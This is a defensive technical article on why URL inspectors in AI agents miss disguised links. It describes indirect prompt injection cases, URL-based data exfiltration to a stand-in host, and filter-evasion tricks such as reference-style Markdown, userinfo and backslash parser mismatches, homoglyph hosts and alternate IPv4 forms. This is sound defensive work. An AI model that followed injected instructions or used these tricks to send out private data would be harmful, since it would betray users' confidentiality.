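# Disguised links in messages read by AI agents: how they escape URL inspection and how to inspect them properly

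## What happens to a link between a message and an agent's request?

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, so that it can open web pages, read mail or send messages. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026) uses a broad definition that includes browsers controlled by a model, chatbots with a search feature, and narrow custom programs that collect product data from shop listings or watch a page for changes. All of these handle links. The emails, chat messages and pages that an agent reads contain web addresses, and the agent writes addresses in its answers to the user and its requests to tools.

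Many products therefore place an inspector between the message and the request. An inspector is software that finds the links in a text and decides whether to allow, remove or flag them. It can miss a link because of how someone wrote it, misread where the link leads, or approve an address that still does harm. Understanding these failures requires knowing the parts of an address, which programs handle it, and in what form.

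### The parts of an address

The IETF (2005), which publishes the internet's technical standards, divides a URI, a category that includes URLs such as `https://mail.example.com/inbox/view?id=42#latest`, into scheme, authority, path, query and fragment. The authority starts after the double slash and ends at the next slash, question mark or number sign. It is usually just a host name, but a user name and an at-sign may precede the host, and a colon and a port number may follow it.

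| Part | In the example | Purpose |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | names the protocol |
| Host | `mail.example.com` | names the server to contact |
| Registrable domain | `example.com` | the part of the host that someone registers and controls |
| Subdomain | `mail` | a name that the domain's holder chose |
| Path | `/inbox/view` | identifies something on that server |
| Query | `id=42` | passes further data, often as a key and a value |
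| Fragment | `latest` | points to a place within the page |

Control over a host name runs from right to left. Whoever registers `example.com` can create `mail.example.com`, or a much longer name, without asking anybody, while `example.com.example.net` belongs to the holder of `example.net`. Software cannot find the registrable domain by counting dots, because each registry has its own policy on the level at which people may register names. It needs a maintained list, such as the one described in Mozilla's *Public Suffix List*. Under that list, the registrable domain of `sub.www.example.com` is `example.com`, whereas `whatwg.github.io` is itself a registrable domain because `github.io` is on the list. Both examples appear in WHATWG's *URL*, the standard for how browsers handle addresses. The standard also warns against treating the registrable domain as a hard security boundary, because the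 list differs between clients.

When a browser requests an address, it contacts the server and sends it the data in the authority, path and query. The browser keeps the fragment for its own use, so the server at `mail.example.com` receives `id=42` but not `latest`. An attacker who wants to send data out inside an address can therefore put it anywhere before the number sign.

### One email on its way through an assistant

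Suppose an employee asks a mail assistant to summarise the morning's messages. One of them comes from a supplier and links to an invoice.

The message arrives as source text, typically HTML, in which tags, comments and styling rules surround the words that the employee would read. An inspector at the mailbox examines this source text or an extract from it, and the source can differ considerably from the displayed text. In October 2026, the security company Barracuda analysed a phishing campaign in which the two differed. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*, text aimed at an AI assistant is usually hidden in HTML comments, passages made invisible by styling, Base64-encoded data and zero-width characters. Even when nothing is hidden, finding where a URL begins and ends in plain text takes guesswork. Writers set URLs off with quotation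 marks, angle brackets or just spaces, as the IETF observes, and adjacent punctuation can be mistaken for part of the URL.

Next, the assistant assembles the model's input. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, call the component that does this the context composer. It joins the system's instructions, the employee's request and the outside content into one flat sequence. The model processes the link as ordinary text in that sequence and does not render the email or parse the address as a browser would. Some assistants also fetch a preview of each address in a conversation and add the linked page's title and description to the sequence, which means they send a request before the model writes anything.

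The model's output can then take two routes. One is an answer to the employee, usually written in Markdown, a plain-text notation for formatting that most chat assistants use. If a second inspector scans the answer, it also works on the raw text, including the notation. A renderer turns the Markdown into what appears on the screen, with clickable links and images. The employee sees the words "March invoice" but no address unless she hovers over them.

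The other route is a tool call, a structured command, such as a request for a web page, that the assistant's software parses and carries out. Tool calls bypass the renderer, and an inspector that scans only answers never receives them.

Either route can end at a fetcher, the component that sends the request. It receives an address without the surrounding text, splits it into its parts and contacts the host. The fetcher may be the employee's browser, a messaging app's preview service, the agent's own tool or a machine that the inspector's designers did not anticipate. In December 2026 the research group Cato AI Labs disclosed three flaws in Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's assistant for office work. None of the leaks depended on the victim's browser. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot*, the requests came from the search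 engine Bing, from a Microsoft service that processes documents in the background, and from code running in a supposedly isolated sandbox. Microsoft had patched all three flaws by mid-November.

### Indirect prompt injection

An assistant that treats an ordinary invoice this way does nothing wrong, but this becomes a problem when the email also contains instructions meant for the model. In indirect prompt injection, someone places instructions in content that an agent reads, and the agent follows them as if its user had given them. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the concept and demonstrated it on Bing's GPT-4 chat, among other systems. The attacker it describes needs no access to the victim's session and can plant text on a page that the assistant is likely to retrieve, or email it to the victim. Microsoft (2025) adds that the text may be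 white on a white background or consist of non-printing characters, but that it needs no special format and can be in a plain text file.

The context composer creates a weakness by joining developer instructions and third-party data into a single natural-language sequence. According to *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, many applications have no reliable way to preserve the boundary between the two. Microsoft trains classifiers to detect injections and marks outside text so that the model can distinguish it, and both measures make injections less likely to succeed. But the company calls deterministic detection an open research problem and designs its products on the assumption that some injections will get through.

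That assumption is the main reason to inspect links. An injection that only changes the tone of a summary is often harmless, but one that steals data needs a way to send it out. In 2025 the programmer Simon Willison described the dangerous combination as access to private data, exposure to malicious text and a way of sending data out. In *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, Willison (2025) expects the same security problem in any system that has all three. Removing any one of them stops the theft. A mail assistant has to read private correspondence, some of it from strangers, so the way of sending data out is almost the only one its makers can realistically remove.

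### Two directions of harm

An incoming link takes the agent or the user to a hostile page. For the user, this is phishing through an assistant. Greshake and colleagues anticipated that assistants could recommend scam sites as trustworthy, with the real address hidden behind friendly link text. They suspected that people would trust a search engine's output more than a suspicious email. In the campaign that Barracuda described, the hidden instructions could lead the assistant to present the phishing message as legitimate or urgent. Microsoft adds that an assistant with permission to send mail could email phishing links to the user's colleagues. Those messages would pass the standard checks against forged senders because they come from the user's account.

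A hostile page is dangerous to an agent because it contains more instructions. A short injection in an email can direct the model to fetch a longer one from elsewhere, so someone who checks only the email will not see the text that ends up steering the agent.

An outgoing link can carry private data to whoever logs the request. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) uses the term URL-based data exfiltration for this. Websites commonly record the addresses that visitors request. If an injected instruction induces an assistant to request `https://example.net/p?city=Leeds`, where Leeds comes from the user's correspondence, the holder of example.net can read the city in the server's log. The data travels with the request, so it leaks whether the server returns a page, a blank image or an error. The leak doesn't depend on what the assistant writes to its user,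 who may see only a faultless summary in the chat.

Microsoft notes that attackers can encode the data so that it isn't readable and put it in the URL's path or a subdomain instead of the query. A subdomain works because the holder of a domain controls every name under it. According to the same post, an image in the answer makes the user's browser send the request without any action by the user, a clickable link requires a click, and a tool call sends the request directly. PromptArmor points out that messaging apps with link previews remove the need for a click.

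The leak has been known since at least early 2023, when the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported it to OpenAI. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he counts dozens of similar vulnerabilities across AI products since then. In July 2026, Willison (2026) covered a case in which researchers extracted a user's name, home city and employer through the page-fetching tool of Anthropic's Claude. Anthropic fixed the vulnerability by stopping the tool from following links found in fetched pages.

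Lan and colleagues measured how often such a leak escapes a check on the assistant's answer. They built a local assistant on qwen2.5:7b, a small open-weight model, put sensitive data into its context, and used a fixed request for a summary to make it preview a malicious page. Their own server recorded the outgoing requests, so they could count actual leaks instead of judging from the model's wording. Over 480 runs, the attack succeeded about 89% of the time, and checks on the output missed 95% of the successes.

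The success rate is a poor guide to commercial products, since the model was small, its system prompt was minimal and the page text reached it unfiltered. The 95% probably generalises better, because it follows from a design in which the check covers the answer but the data leaves through a tool call. The same team also split the sensitive data over several requests, which reduced their measure of leakage through any single request by 73% and defeated simple data-loss filters. An inspector that judges each address by itself therefore examines only fragments of the data. The address may even contain none of it. Microsoft notes that if an injected instruction makes a tool call depend on some private fact, the mere occurrence of the call reveals one bit.

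For an incoming link, an inspector has to establish who controls the destination and what is there. For an outgoing link, it has to establish what the address contains and where that content came from, which a list of known phishing sites can't show. OpenAI makes this distinction when describing its own safeguard, which aims to stop quiet leaks through the address itself but doesn't guarantee that the page is trustworthy. An attack can easily use both, with an incoming link that delivers the instructions and an outgoing one that sends out the result.

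### The condition for sound inspection

An inspector's verdicts are worth something only if it finds every link that the renderer or a fetcher will use, and reads each address as the fetcher will. In symbols, let $F$ be the set of addresses that renderers and fetchers will use because of a given text or tool call, and $I$ the set that the inspector extracts. Sound inspection requires

$$F \subseteq I \quad \text{and} \quad \text{parse}_{\text{inspector}}(u) = \text{parse}_{\text{fetcher}}(u) \ \text{ for every } u \in F.$$

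An inspector that meets this minimum must still decide whether the host is trustworthy and whether `42` is an invoice number or part of someone's password. If it doesn't meet the minimum, it is evaluating the wrong thing, however carefully the list of permitted domains was chosen.

An inspector that must find every link can tolerate mistaking a harmless string for a link, which only causes a false alarm, but any link it misses goes through unchecked. A filter in Microsoft 365 Copilot recognised the most familiar Markdown notation for links but missed a lesser-known one, a flaw that Microsoft had already fixed when Willison described it in June 2025. The set $F$ also depends on where people read the answer, because one app's renderer can request an address that another's withholds, even when the answer is identical. OpenAI introduced a link check in ChatGPT in December 2023, but Rehberger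 later found that some places, including the macOS and iOS apps, lacked it entirely. OpenAI added further mitigations around August 2025.

An inspector cannot err on the side of caution when it parses an address, except by refusing every address that two programs might read differently. For example, `%2F` in an address is the percent-encoded form of a slash that is data, not a separator. The IETF therefore requires software to split an address into its components before decoding them. An inspector that decodes first will find a separator where the fetcher finds none, so it will approve or refuse an address with different parts from the one requested. This is a parser mismatch, in which two programs read the same text or address differently, so that one checks something other than what the other uses.

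## Which ways of writing a link does a simple filter miss?

Programmers writing a link filter usually start with the most familiar Markdown notation, `[March invoice](https://example.com/march)`. Markdown has eight more ways to attach an address to text, and messaging apps such as Slack add their own. Microsoft 365 Copilot's filter missed reference-style links.

Markdown also has no single definition. John Gruber released it in 2004 as a description of the syntax and a Perl script that converted it to HTML. His description left many cases undefined, including which address applies when a text defines the same label twice, and dozens of implementations handled them differently. *CommonMark Spec* (MacFarlane, 2024) settles these cases with exact rules and about 650 worked examples. GitHub (2019) based its dialect, GitHub Flavored Markdown (GFM), on an earlier version of CommonMark.

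### The forms of a link in Markdown

An inline link has its visible text in square brackets and its destination in parentheses directly afterwards. The visible text can be empty, or contain further brackets if they balance, as in `[March [final] invoice](https://example.com/march)`. The destination can start on the line below the opening parenthesis. If it contains spaces, it needs angle brackets:

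```
[March invoice](<https://example.com/march invoice>)
```

The angle brackets are optional for an address without spaces. In both cases the renderer removes them, so they aren't part of the address.

An image uses the same notation with an exclamation mark in front, `![logo](https://example.com/logo.png)`. The words in brackets become its description. Because the visible text of a link may contain an image, a clickable logo has two destinations, one that the browser loads and one that it opens after a click:

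```
[![logo](https://example.com/logo.png)](https://example.com/home)
```

A reference-style link replaces the address with a label. The address is in a definition elsewhere in the text, which consists of the label in brackets, a colon and the destination. There are three forms:

```
[March invoice][inv]
[inv][]
[inv]

[inv]: https://example.com/march
```

The first line is a full reference, with visible text followed by a label. The second is a collapsed reference, in which the label is also the visible text and is followed by empty brackets. The third is a shortcut reference, which omits the empty brackets. It looks like any other bracketed word, and is a link only if the text contains a matching definition. Images can use all three forms.

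An autolink is an address in angle brackets, such as `<https://example.com/march>`. CommonMark accepts any scheme, registered or not, that starts with a letter and has 2 to 32 characters, so `<localhost:5001/foo>` becomes a link with the scheme `localhost`. An email address in angle brackets becomes a `mailto:` link.

A bare URL is an address without any markup. CommonMark leaves it as ordinary text, while GFM turns it into a link.

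Finally, Markdown can contain HTML, and a CommonMark parser passes the tags through unchanged:

```
<a href="https://example.com/march">March invoice</a>
```

In an HTML link tag, the address can be in double quotes, single quotes or no quotes, with or without spaces around the equals sign. Whether the reader sees a link depends on how the product handles the HTML. GitHub, for example, cleans it after converting the Markdown, and other products show the tags as text.

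### How a label finds its address

To resolve a reference-style link, an inspector has to match labels exactly as the renderer does. Before comparing labels, a CommonMark parser removes the outer brackets, strips spaces from both ends, reduces every run of spaces and line breaks to a single space, and applies Unicode case folding so that capital and small letters match. `[March Invoice]` therefore matches a definition for `[march   invoice]`.

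Case folding differs slightly from converting to lower case. In MacFarlane's example, the German capital `ẞ` matches `SS` under case folding. Lower-casing turns them into `ß` and `ss`, which don't match, so an inspector that uses it would treat the label as undefined and miss the link.

If two definitions share a label, the first one applies:

```
[March invoice][inv]

[inv]: https://example.net/a
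[INV]: https://example.com/b
```

The renderer links to example.net here. An inspector that stores definitions in a lookup table, where each new entry replaces the old one, would check example.com instead. MacFarlane recommends, but doesn't require, that a parser warn about such duplicates.

A definition can come after the link that uses it, as in this example, and it is invisible in the rendered text. A definition inside a list or a quotation still applies to the whole document. So if an assistant's answer quotes an email passage that contains a definition for `[invoice]`, a bracketed `[invoice]` in the assistant's own sentence becomes a link to the URL in that definition.

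An inspector that scans for lines starting with a bracketed label and a colon will mistake some code and ordinary text for link definitions. A line is code if it is indented by four spaces or is inside a fenced code block. A definition also can't begin in the middle of a paragraph, and any text after its optional title makes the whole line ordinary text.

Unlike other false alarms, this one can make the inspector miss a real link. If the inspector accepts an indented line as the first definition of a label, it will ignore the later definition that the renderer uses. The simplest protection is to check the address in every possible definition, without working out which one applies.

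A filter can also miss a link because of the precedence rules. In `[March invoice](see below)`, the words in parentheses can't be a destination because they contain a space without angle brackets. A filter would find no address there and skip the text. But if the text defines the label `march invoice`, the bracketed words are a shortcut reference, and the reader sees a working link followed by "(see below)".

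### Escapes and character references

A destination in the source text doesn't have to look like the final address. In an inline link or a definition, a backslash before a punctuation character disappears, and an HTML character reference becomes the character it stands for. Under CommonMark, these three links have the same destination:

```
[March invoice](https://example.com/march)
[March invoice](https://example\.com/march)
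[March invoice](https://example&#46;com/march)
```

An inspector that looks up the raw string in a list of blocked domains will find only the first. Backslashes have no special effect in autolinks or HTML attributes, so an inspector that removes them everywhere will get those addresses wrong. A Markdown parser should also leave percent-encoding such as `%2E` as it is, and let the program that reads the address do any decoding.

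A character reference can't replace a character that gives the text its structure. If someone writes `&#91;` for an opening square bracket, the reader sees a bracket but no link. This helps the inspector, because the brackets that form a Markdown link always appear literally in the source, though the address may not.

### Where a bare URL ends

In GitHub Flavored Markdown (GFM), a string that begins with `http://`, `https://` or `www.` becomes a link at the start of a line, after a space, or after `*`, `_`, `~` or `(`. The parser adds `http://` to addresses that start with `www.`. The host must contain at least one full stop, and its last two parts can't contain an underscore.

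The address continues until a space or a `<`. The parser then removes characters from the end that probably belong to the sentence.

| Text | Address of the link | Rule |
|---|---|---|
| `Visit https://example.com/a.b.` | `https://example.com/a.b` | drop `?`, `!`, `.`, `,`, `:`, `*`, `_` or `~` at the end |
| `(see https://example.com/a_(b))` | `https://example.com/a_(b)` | drop closing parentheses that have no partner |
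| `https://example.com/?q=(b))+ok` | `https://example.com/?q=(b))+ok` | count parentheses only if the address ends in one |
| `https://example.com/?q=a&hl;` | `https://example.com/?q=a` | drop an ending that looks like a character reference |
| `https://example.com/he<lp` | `https://example.com/he` | stop at `<` |

Parsers differ in how they recognize links. The GFM specification doesn't list quotation marks as trailing punctuation, but Marked's *fix*, a proposed change to a JavaScript parser, notes that the implementation removes them anyway. The grammar for micromark, another JavaScript parser, also counts them as trailing punctuation, according to npm trends' *micromark extension gfm autolink literal*. The Haskell parser commonmark-hs departs from the rule on trailing punctuation by design, as commonmark-hs' *autolinks.md* notes. GitHub itself uses two algorithms, one during parsing and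 one afterwards, according to unified's *micromark/micromark-extension-gfm-autolink-literal*.

These disagreements are usually minor, since an extra quotation mark at the end of a path doesn't change the host, but they matter when an inspector compares complete addresses with a list of approved ones. A much more serious problem arises if the inspector follows plain CommonMark and misses a link that a GFM renderer creates.

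### Slack's notation

Slack calls its own notation mrkdwn. It puts the destination first, then a vertical bar and the visible text:

```
<https://example.com/march|March invoice>
```

According to Slack's *Formatting message text*, the server also turns bare URLs into links, and an app that retrieves the message receives them in angle brackets. An agent that reads a Slack channel this way therefore gets different text from what the sender typed.

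Slack advises developers to find everything between `<` and `>` and classify it by its first characters. `#C` marks a channel, `@U` or `@W` a user, and `!` a group mention or a special command. Anything else is a link. This method catches links that a search for `https://` misses, such as `<example.com|Fred Enriquez>`, an example from Slack that has no scheme.

But the procedure can still miss an address. Slack has a command that displays a date in the reader's time zone, and the date can carry a link:

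```
<!date^1392734382^{date_short}^https://example.com/|Feb 18, 2014 PST>
```

In Slack, a formatted date can include a link, as in `<!date^timestamp^format^link|fallback>`. A simple filter misses this link if it checks only the angle-bracketed items that don't start with `@`, `#` or `!`. It also misses links in buttons, because a button's address is in a separate `url` field and not in the message text.

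Slack decodes only three character references, those for `&`, `<` and `>`, while CommonMark decodes numeric references and every named reference in HTML. The address `https://example&#46;com/march` from the earlier example is therefore a different address in each notation.

Agents on Slack often have to handle standard Markdown as well as mrkdwn. In February 2025, Slack introduced a message block that accepts standard Markdown and converts it, intended for apps with AI features (Slack, 2025). According to Slack's *Markdown block*, the block supports inline links and turns images into text links. The page's list of supported elements doesn't mention reference-style links, so a developer would have to test how the block handles them. An agent may therefore read links in mrkdwn and write them in Markdown within the same conversation, and an inspector built for one notation won't work for the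 other.

### A regular expression and ten links

A regular expression is a compact pattern for searching text. A typical one for inline links is:

```
\[([^\]]+)\]\((https?://[^\s)]+)\)
```

It looks for an opening square bracket, at least one character that isn't a closing bracket, and then `](`. After that it expects `http://` or `https://`, followed by characters other than spaces and closing parentheses, and finally a closing parenthesis. The following text has one link of each kind, with three definitions at the end:

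```
[Invoice 1](https://example.com/1)
[Invoice 2](<https://example.com/2>)
[Invoice 3][third]
[Invoice 4][]
[Invoice 5]
<https://example.com/6>
https://example.com/7
![Invoice 8](https://example.com/8)
<a href="https://example.com/9">Invoice 9</a>
<https://example.com/10|Invoice 10>

[third]: https://example.com/3
[invoice 4]: https://example.com/4
[invoice 5]: https://example.com/5
```

The expression finds two of the ten.

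| Line | Form | Found? | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | inline link | yes | fits the pattern |
| 2 | inline link with a bracketed destination | no | `<` comes before `https` |
| 3 | full reference | no | a label follows the text, not a parenthesis |
| 4 | collapsed reference | no | empty brackets follow the text |
| 5 | shortcut reference | no | nothing follows the text |
| 6 | autolink | no | has no square brackets |
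| 7 | bare URL | no | has no markup |
| 8 | image | yes | the match starts after the exclamation mark, so the filter takes the image for an ordinary link |
| 9 | raw HTML link | no | the address is in an attribute |
| 10 | Slack link | no | the address comes before the text |

The result for line 8 is less reassuring than it looks, since a filter that allows links because they need a click would also allow the image, which the browser loads without one.

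This expression mishandles even some ordinary inline links. It misses `[March [final] invoice](https://example.com/march)` because of the inner brackets, and it misses any link whose address starts on a new line. From `[March invoice](https://example.com/march_(final)_v2)` it extracts only `https://example.com/march_(final`, because it stops at the first closing parenthesis. In the clickable logo shown earlier, it finds the address of the image but not the address of the page that opens after a click.

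A simple filter can ignore the markup and search for anything that starts with a web scheme, for example with `https?://\S+`, which takes every character up to the next space. In the sample text, this pattern finds all ten addresses, but six of the matches include extra characters, such as a closing parenthesis or part of an HTML tag. The pattern also misses `www.example.com`, Slack links without a scheme, and addresses such as `https&#58;//example.com/march`, where a character reference replaces the colon.

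A broad search like this is a useful backup to a parser because it may find addresses in notation the parser doesn't support, but it isn't reliable enough to approve a link. Adding patterns for more forms wouldn't cover every case, because regular expressions in the strict sense can't match brackets nested to an arbitrary depth or determine which of several definitions the renderer will use. An inspector that handled all of this would amount to a Markdown parser, and well-tested ones already exist.

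### The same text as a tree

A Markdown parser turns text into a tree in which each paragraph, link or image is a node. CommonMark describes this process in two phases. The parser first reads all the lines, divides them into blocks such as paragraphs and quotations, and records any link definitions. It then looks for links inside the paragraphs. Because it already knows every definition by then, a link can come before its definition.

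With the GFM extension for bare URLs switched on, the sample text produces roughly this tree, without the line breaks:

```
document
└─ paragraph
   ├─ link   "Invoice 1"              → https://example.com/1
   ├─ link   "Invoice 2"              → https://example.com/2
   ├─ link   "Invoice 3"              → https://example.com/3
   ├─ link   "Invoice 4"              → https://example.com/4
   ├─ link   "Invoice 5"              → https://example.com/5
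   ├─ link   "https://example.com/6"  → https://example.com/6
   ├─ link   "https://example.com/7"  → https://example.com/7
   ├─ image  "Invoice 8"              → https://example.com/8
   ├─ html   <a href="https://example.com/9">
   ├─ text   "Invoice 9"
   ├─ html   </a>
   └─ text   "<https://example.com/10|Invoice 10>"
```

An inspector can read the first eight destinations directly from the nodes, with the escapes and character references already decoded. The tree also distinguishes the image from the links. For line 9, the inspector has to pass the tag to an HTML parser and read the `href` attribute. A Markdown parser treats line 10 as ordinary text, so the inspector has to parse it using Slack's rules.

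Some parsers leave the developer to match reference-style links with their definitions. The tree format mdast, common in JavaScript tools, stores these links and definitions as separate kinds of nodes. A developer who collects only nodes of type `link` will miss the same three lines as the regular expression.

A tree is also a convenient place to inspect outgoing messages. Chat SDK's *Markdown* describes a chatbot toolkit that holds every message as an mdast tree and converts it to each platform's notation at the end. Inspecting the tree before that conversion requires only one set of rules, but it misses links that the platform creates later, such as when Slack's server turns a bare URL into a link.

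### When the visible text names another address

Neither Markdown nor HTML requires the visible text of a link to agree with its destination:

```
[https://example.com/login](https://example.net/login)
```

The user sees an address at example.com, but a click leads to example.net. A model that receives the source text gets both addresses, while the user sees only the first unless she hovers over the link. A link can also have a title, which many programs show as a tooltip, and that title may contain an address other than the link's destination.

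The broad search for `https?://\S+` also fails on this link. The two addresses have no space between them, so the search returns everything from the first `https` to the final parenthesis as one string. If the inspector parses that string as a URL, the host is `example.com` and the rest becomes part of the path. The inspector never examines `example.net`, the only host the browser will contact. The narrower expression reads this particular link correctly.

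Once a parser has separated a link's visible text from its destination, an inspector can easily check for a mismatch if the text is an address. It compares the two hosts or, more tolerantly, the two registrable domains. A mismatch doesn't prove fraud, because newsletters routinely send clicks through a tracking service before the reader reaches the advertised page. If the visible text is just "March invoice", there is no address to compare. A mismatch is therefore a helpful warning sign, but the inspector still needs to check the destination.

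### When conversion removes the destination

A model can't judge a destination that it never receives. Many assistants convert HTML mail to plain text before passing it to the model, because the markup takes up space and adds little to a summary. The simplest converter deletes all tags and keeps the text between them. Suppose an email contains these two links:

```
<a href="https://example.net/pay">March invoice</a>
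<a href="https://example.net/login">https://example.com/login</a>
```

The result is:

```
March invoice
https://example.com/login
```

The conversion removes the first address, so if the user asks whether the invoice link is safe, the model can only judge the words around it. The second case is worse because the remaining address looks like the link's destination. An assistant could accurately report that the text contains a link to example.com, and an inspector that runs on the converted text could approve it, even though the link in the user's mail program leads to example.net.

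The same can happen with chat messages. The Chat SDK documentation on unpkg describes a function that strips all formatting and returns plain text. That output is fine for a search index, but if the function drops link addresses along with the formatting, an inspector can't check them.

Other converters keep each address by writing it in parentheses after the visible text, which makes the input longer. Whichever converter is used, an inspector should read the original HTML. Emails often include both a plain-text version and an HTML version, and the two can contain different links, so the plain-text version is weak evidence of what the user will click on.

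### What a parser doesn't solve

A parser gives the right answer only for its own dialect. GitHub (2017) complained that very similar Markdown documents could produce "wildly different outputs" depending on the parser. The specifications have reduced this problem, but programs still follow different versions of them. Consider this line:

```
Thanks <!-- draft -- [March invoice](https://example.com/march) -->
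```

Under the 2024 version of CommonMark, everything from `<!--` to `-->` is an HTML comment, which a browser doesn't show. Under the 2019 GFM specification, a comment can't contain two hyphens in a row, so a span that contains them is ordinary text and a link inside it works. An inspector built on the newer rules would miss a link that a renderer built on the older rules shows.

Slack's notation can cause a similar mismatch, in which two programs both find a link but read different addresses from it. In `<https://example.com/march|invoice>`, Slack takes the part before the bar as the destination. CommonMark allows a vertical bar in an autolink, so a CommonMark parser treats the whole string between the angle brackets as the address.

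Such differences are hard to notice in testing. As MacFarlane points out, nothing in Markdown counts as a syntax error, so a parser with the wrong rules produces a plausible result without warning. The best remedy is to inspect the parse tree that the renderer will use. This is straightforward when one company controls both the filter and the renderer, but an assistant whose answers appear on a website, in a phone app and in Slack may have three renderers.

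Streaming adds a timing problem. Most chat assistants show an answer while the model is still writing it, and many renderers parse the text again whenever a new piece arrives. If the first piece contains `![chart][c]` and the last one contains `[c]: https://example.com/chart.png`, the reader at first sees only bracketed text. When the definition arrives, the renderer turns the bracketed text into an image, and the browser requests the address.

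If a link is split between pieces of a streamed answer, an inspector that checks each piece separately never finds a complete link. An inspector that waits for the whole answer can find it, but by then the browser may already have sent the request. The inspector therefore has to parse all the text received so far each time a piece arrives, and the renderer must not display the new piece until that check has finished.

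## How can one address be read as two destinations?

After extracting a link's destination, an inspector still has to work out which host a fetcher will contact. Some addresses mislead a person or a language model even though every correct parser reads them the same way. Others cause two parsers to extract different hosts. A server can also redirect the fetcher to another host, so the inspector checks only the first one.

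### A familiar name in the wrong place

The user name that may precede the host in an address is meant for logging in and has no influence on where the request goes:

```
https://example.com@example.net/invoice
```

In `https://example.com@example.net/`, the host is `example.net`, and `example.com` is only a user name. Berners-Lee, Fielding and Masinter (2005) warn about this in *Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)*, the IETF standard also known as RFC 3986. People rarely use a user name in an address, so they easily mistake it for the host, and an attacker can make it long enough to push the real host out of view.

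The WHATWG standard for browsers classes addresses that include login details as invalid, but has parsers record an error and continue. If the authority contains several at-signs, the host starts after the last one. A home-made check that splits the authority at its at-signs and takes the second piece would read `https://user@example.com@example.net/` as a link to example.com, while a browser would go to example.net.

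A familiar name can also be a subdomain, as in this host:

```
example.com.invoices.example.net
```

To find out who controls it, an inspector compares each ending of the name with the Public Suffix List.

| Ending | On the list? |
|---|---|
| `net` | yes |
| `example.net` | no |
| `invoices.example.net` | no |
| `com.invoices.example.net` | no |
| `example.com.invoices.example.net` | no |

The public suffix is the longest ending of the hostname that appears on the Public Suffix List, here `net`. The registrable domain is the suffix plus the label to its left, here `example.net`.

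Suppose the holder of `example.net` rents out subdomains to customers and has the domain added to the list, as happened with `github.io`. The longest listed ending is then `example.net`, and the registrable domain becomes `invoices.example.net`, which a customer controls. An inspector with an outdated copy of the list would treat all the customers as one party, so approving one would approve the rest.

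Comparing the result with a list of permitted or blocked domains can also fail. A test for whether a host ends in `bank.example` also accepts `notbank.example`, unless it requires a dot before the match. A host name may also end in a dot. WHATWG treats `example.com.` and `example.com` as different hosts, although both normally lead to the same server, so a blocklist that contains only `example.com` misses the version with the trailing dot.

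### Look-alike characters and Punycode

WHATWG gives examples of characters that readers confuse: the digit 1 with a small l or capital I, the letters rn with m, and the Latin a with the Cyrillic а. Some Unicode characters that control text direction are invisible.

The domain name system works with ASCII names, so software converts any other characters before looking up a host. The converted label starts with `xn--`, followed by an encoding called Punycode:

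| Host as displayed | Host as looked up |
|---|---|
| `bank.example` | `bank.example` |
| `bаnk.example`, with a Cyrillic а | `xn--bnk-6cd.example` |

Punycode keeps the ASCII letters in order, then adds a hyphen and a code for the remaining character and its position. Once an inspector has converted both names, an exact comparison will tell them apart. Anyone who judges the name by its appearance can still mistake one for the other, and so can an inspector that compares the names before converting them.

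Every legitimate name in Arabic script has the `xn--` prefix, so the prefix doesn't indicate fraud. A name without it can still be deceptive. For example, `rnail.example` imitates `mail.example` using only ASCII letters.

Converting a domain name to ASCII can produce two destinations, depending on the rules used. Under WHATWG's rules, `faß.example` becomes `xn--fa-hia.example`. RFC 3986 refers to an older set of rules, which replace ß with ss, giving `fass.example`. Different people could register those two names, so an inspector with an old conversion library might check one site while the browser opens the other.

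### Encoded host names and numeric addresses

Browsers decode percent-encoding in the host, so `https://exam%70le.org` leads to example.org, but a search of the raw text for `example.org` misses it. RFC 3986 also allows percent-encoding in the host, but requires software that creates addresses to use it only for non-ASCII characters.

The rule of splitting an address before decoding it applies to the host too. In `https://exa%23mple.org`, the code `%23` stands for a number sign. A browser that follows the rule rejects the address, because a host can't contain a number sign. An inspector that decodes the whole address before splitting it treats everything after the number sign as a fragment and reports the host as `exa`.

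Instead of a name, the host can be a numeric IP address. An IPv4 address is a 32-bit number that people usually write as four bytes, $a.b.c.d$, with the value

$$N = a \cdot 256^3 + b \cdot 256^2 + c \cdot 256 + d.$$

Browsers accept other ways of writing the same number. All of these lead to 192.0.2.1, an address reserved for documentation:

| Host in the link | How a browser reads it |
|---|---|
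| `192.0.2.1` | four decimal bytes |
| `3221225985` | the whole number in decimal |
| `0xC0000201` | the whole number in hexadecimal |
| `0300.0.2.1` | a leading zero marks an octal number, and octal 300 is 192 |
| `192.513` | the last part fills the remaining three bytes |

RFC 3986 recognises an IPv4 address only when it is written as four decimal numbers separated by dots, and treats other forms as names. But it warns that many programs pass the host to operating-system routines that accept those other forms. Leading zeros are especially ambiguous. A program that reads `010` as octal takes `192.0.2.010` for 192.0.2.8, while one that ignores the leading zero takes it for 192.0.2.10.

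These forms matter most for server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker makes a server send a request to a machine the attacker can't reach directly. An agent's page-fetching tool is an obvious target if it runs inside a company's network. Many inspectors therefore block internal addresses such as `127.0.0.1`, which a machine uses to contact itself. A filter that looks for text starting with `127.` misses the same address written as a single number. RFC 3986 advises converting the host to its numeric value and filtering on that value.

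### Two standards and two hosts

RFC 3986 defines which strings are valid addresses. The WHATWG standard also defines what a browser should do with invalid ones, and it often repairs them. The difference is clearest with a backslash:

```
https://example.com\@example.net/
```

| Part | WHATWG | Splitting by the RFC 3986 delimiters |
|---|---|---|
| Where the authority ends | at the backslash, which counts as a slash | at the next `/`, `?` or `#` |
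| User name | none | `example.com\` |
| Host | `example.com` | `example.net` |
| Path | `/@example.net/` | `/` |

A strict RFC 3986 parser would reject this address, because the grammar has no place for a backslash. But the standard also includes a regular expression for splitting well-formed addresses into their parts, which doesn't check whether an address is well formed. Software that uses it on untrusted text gets the result in the right-hand column of the table. If the inspector reads the address one way and the fetcher reads it the other way, the inspector checks a host that the fetcher never contacts.

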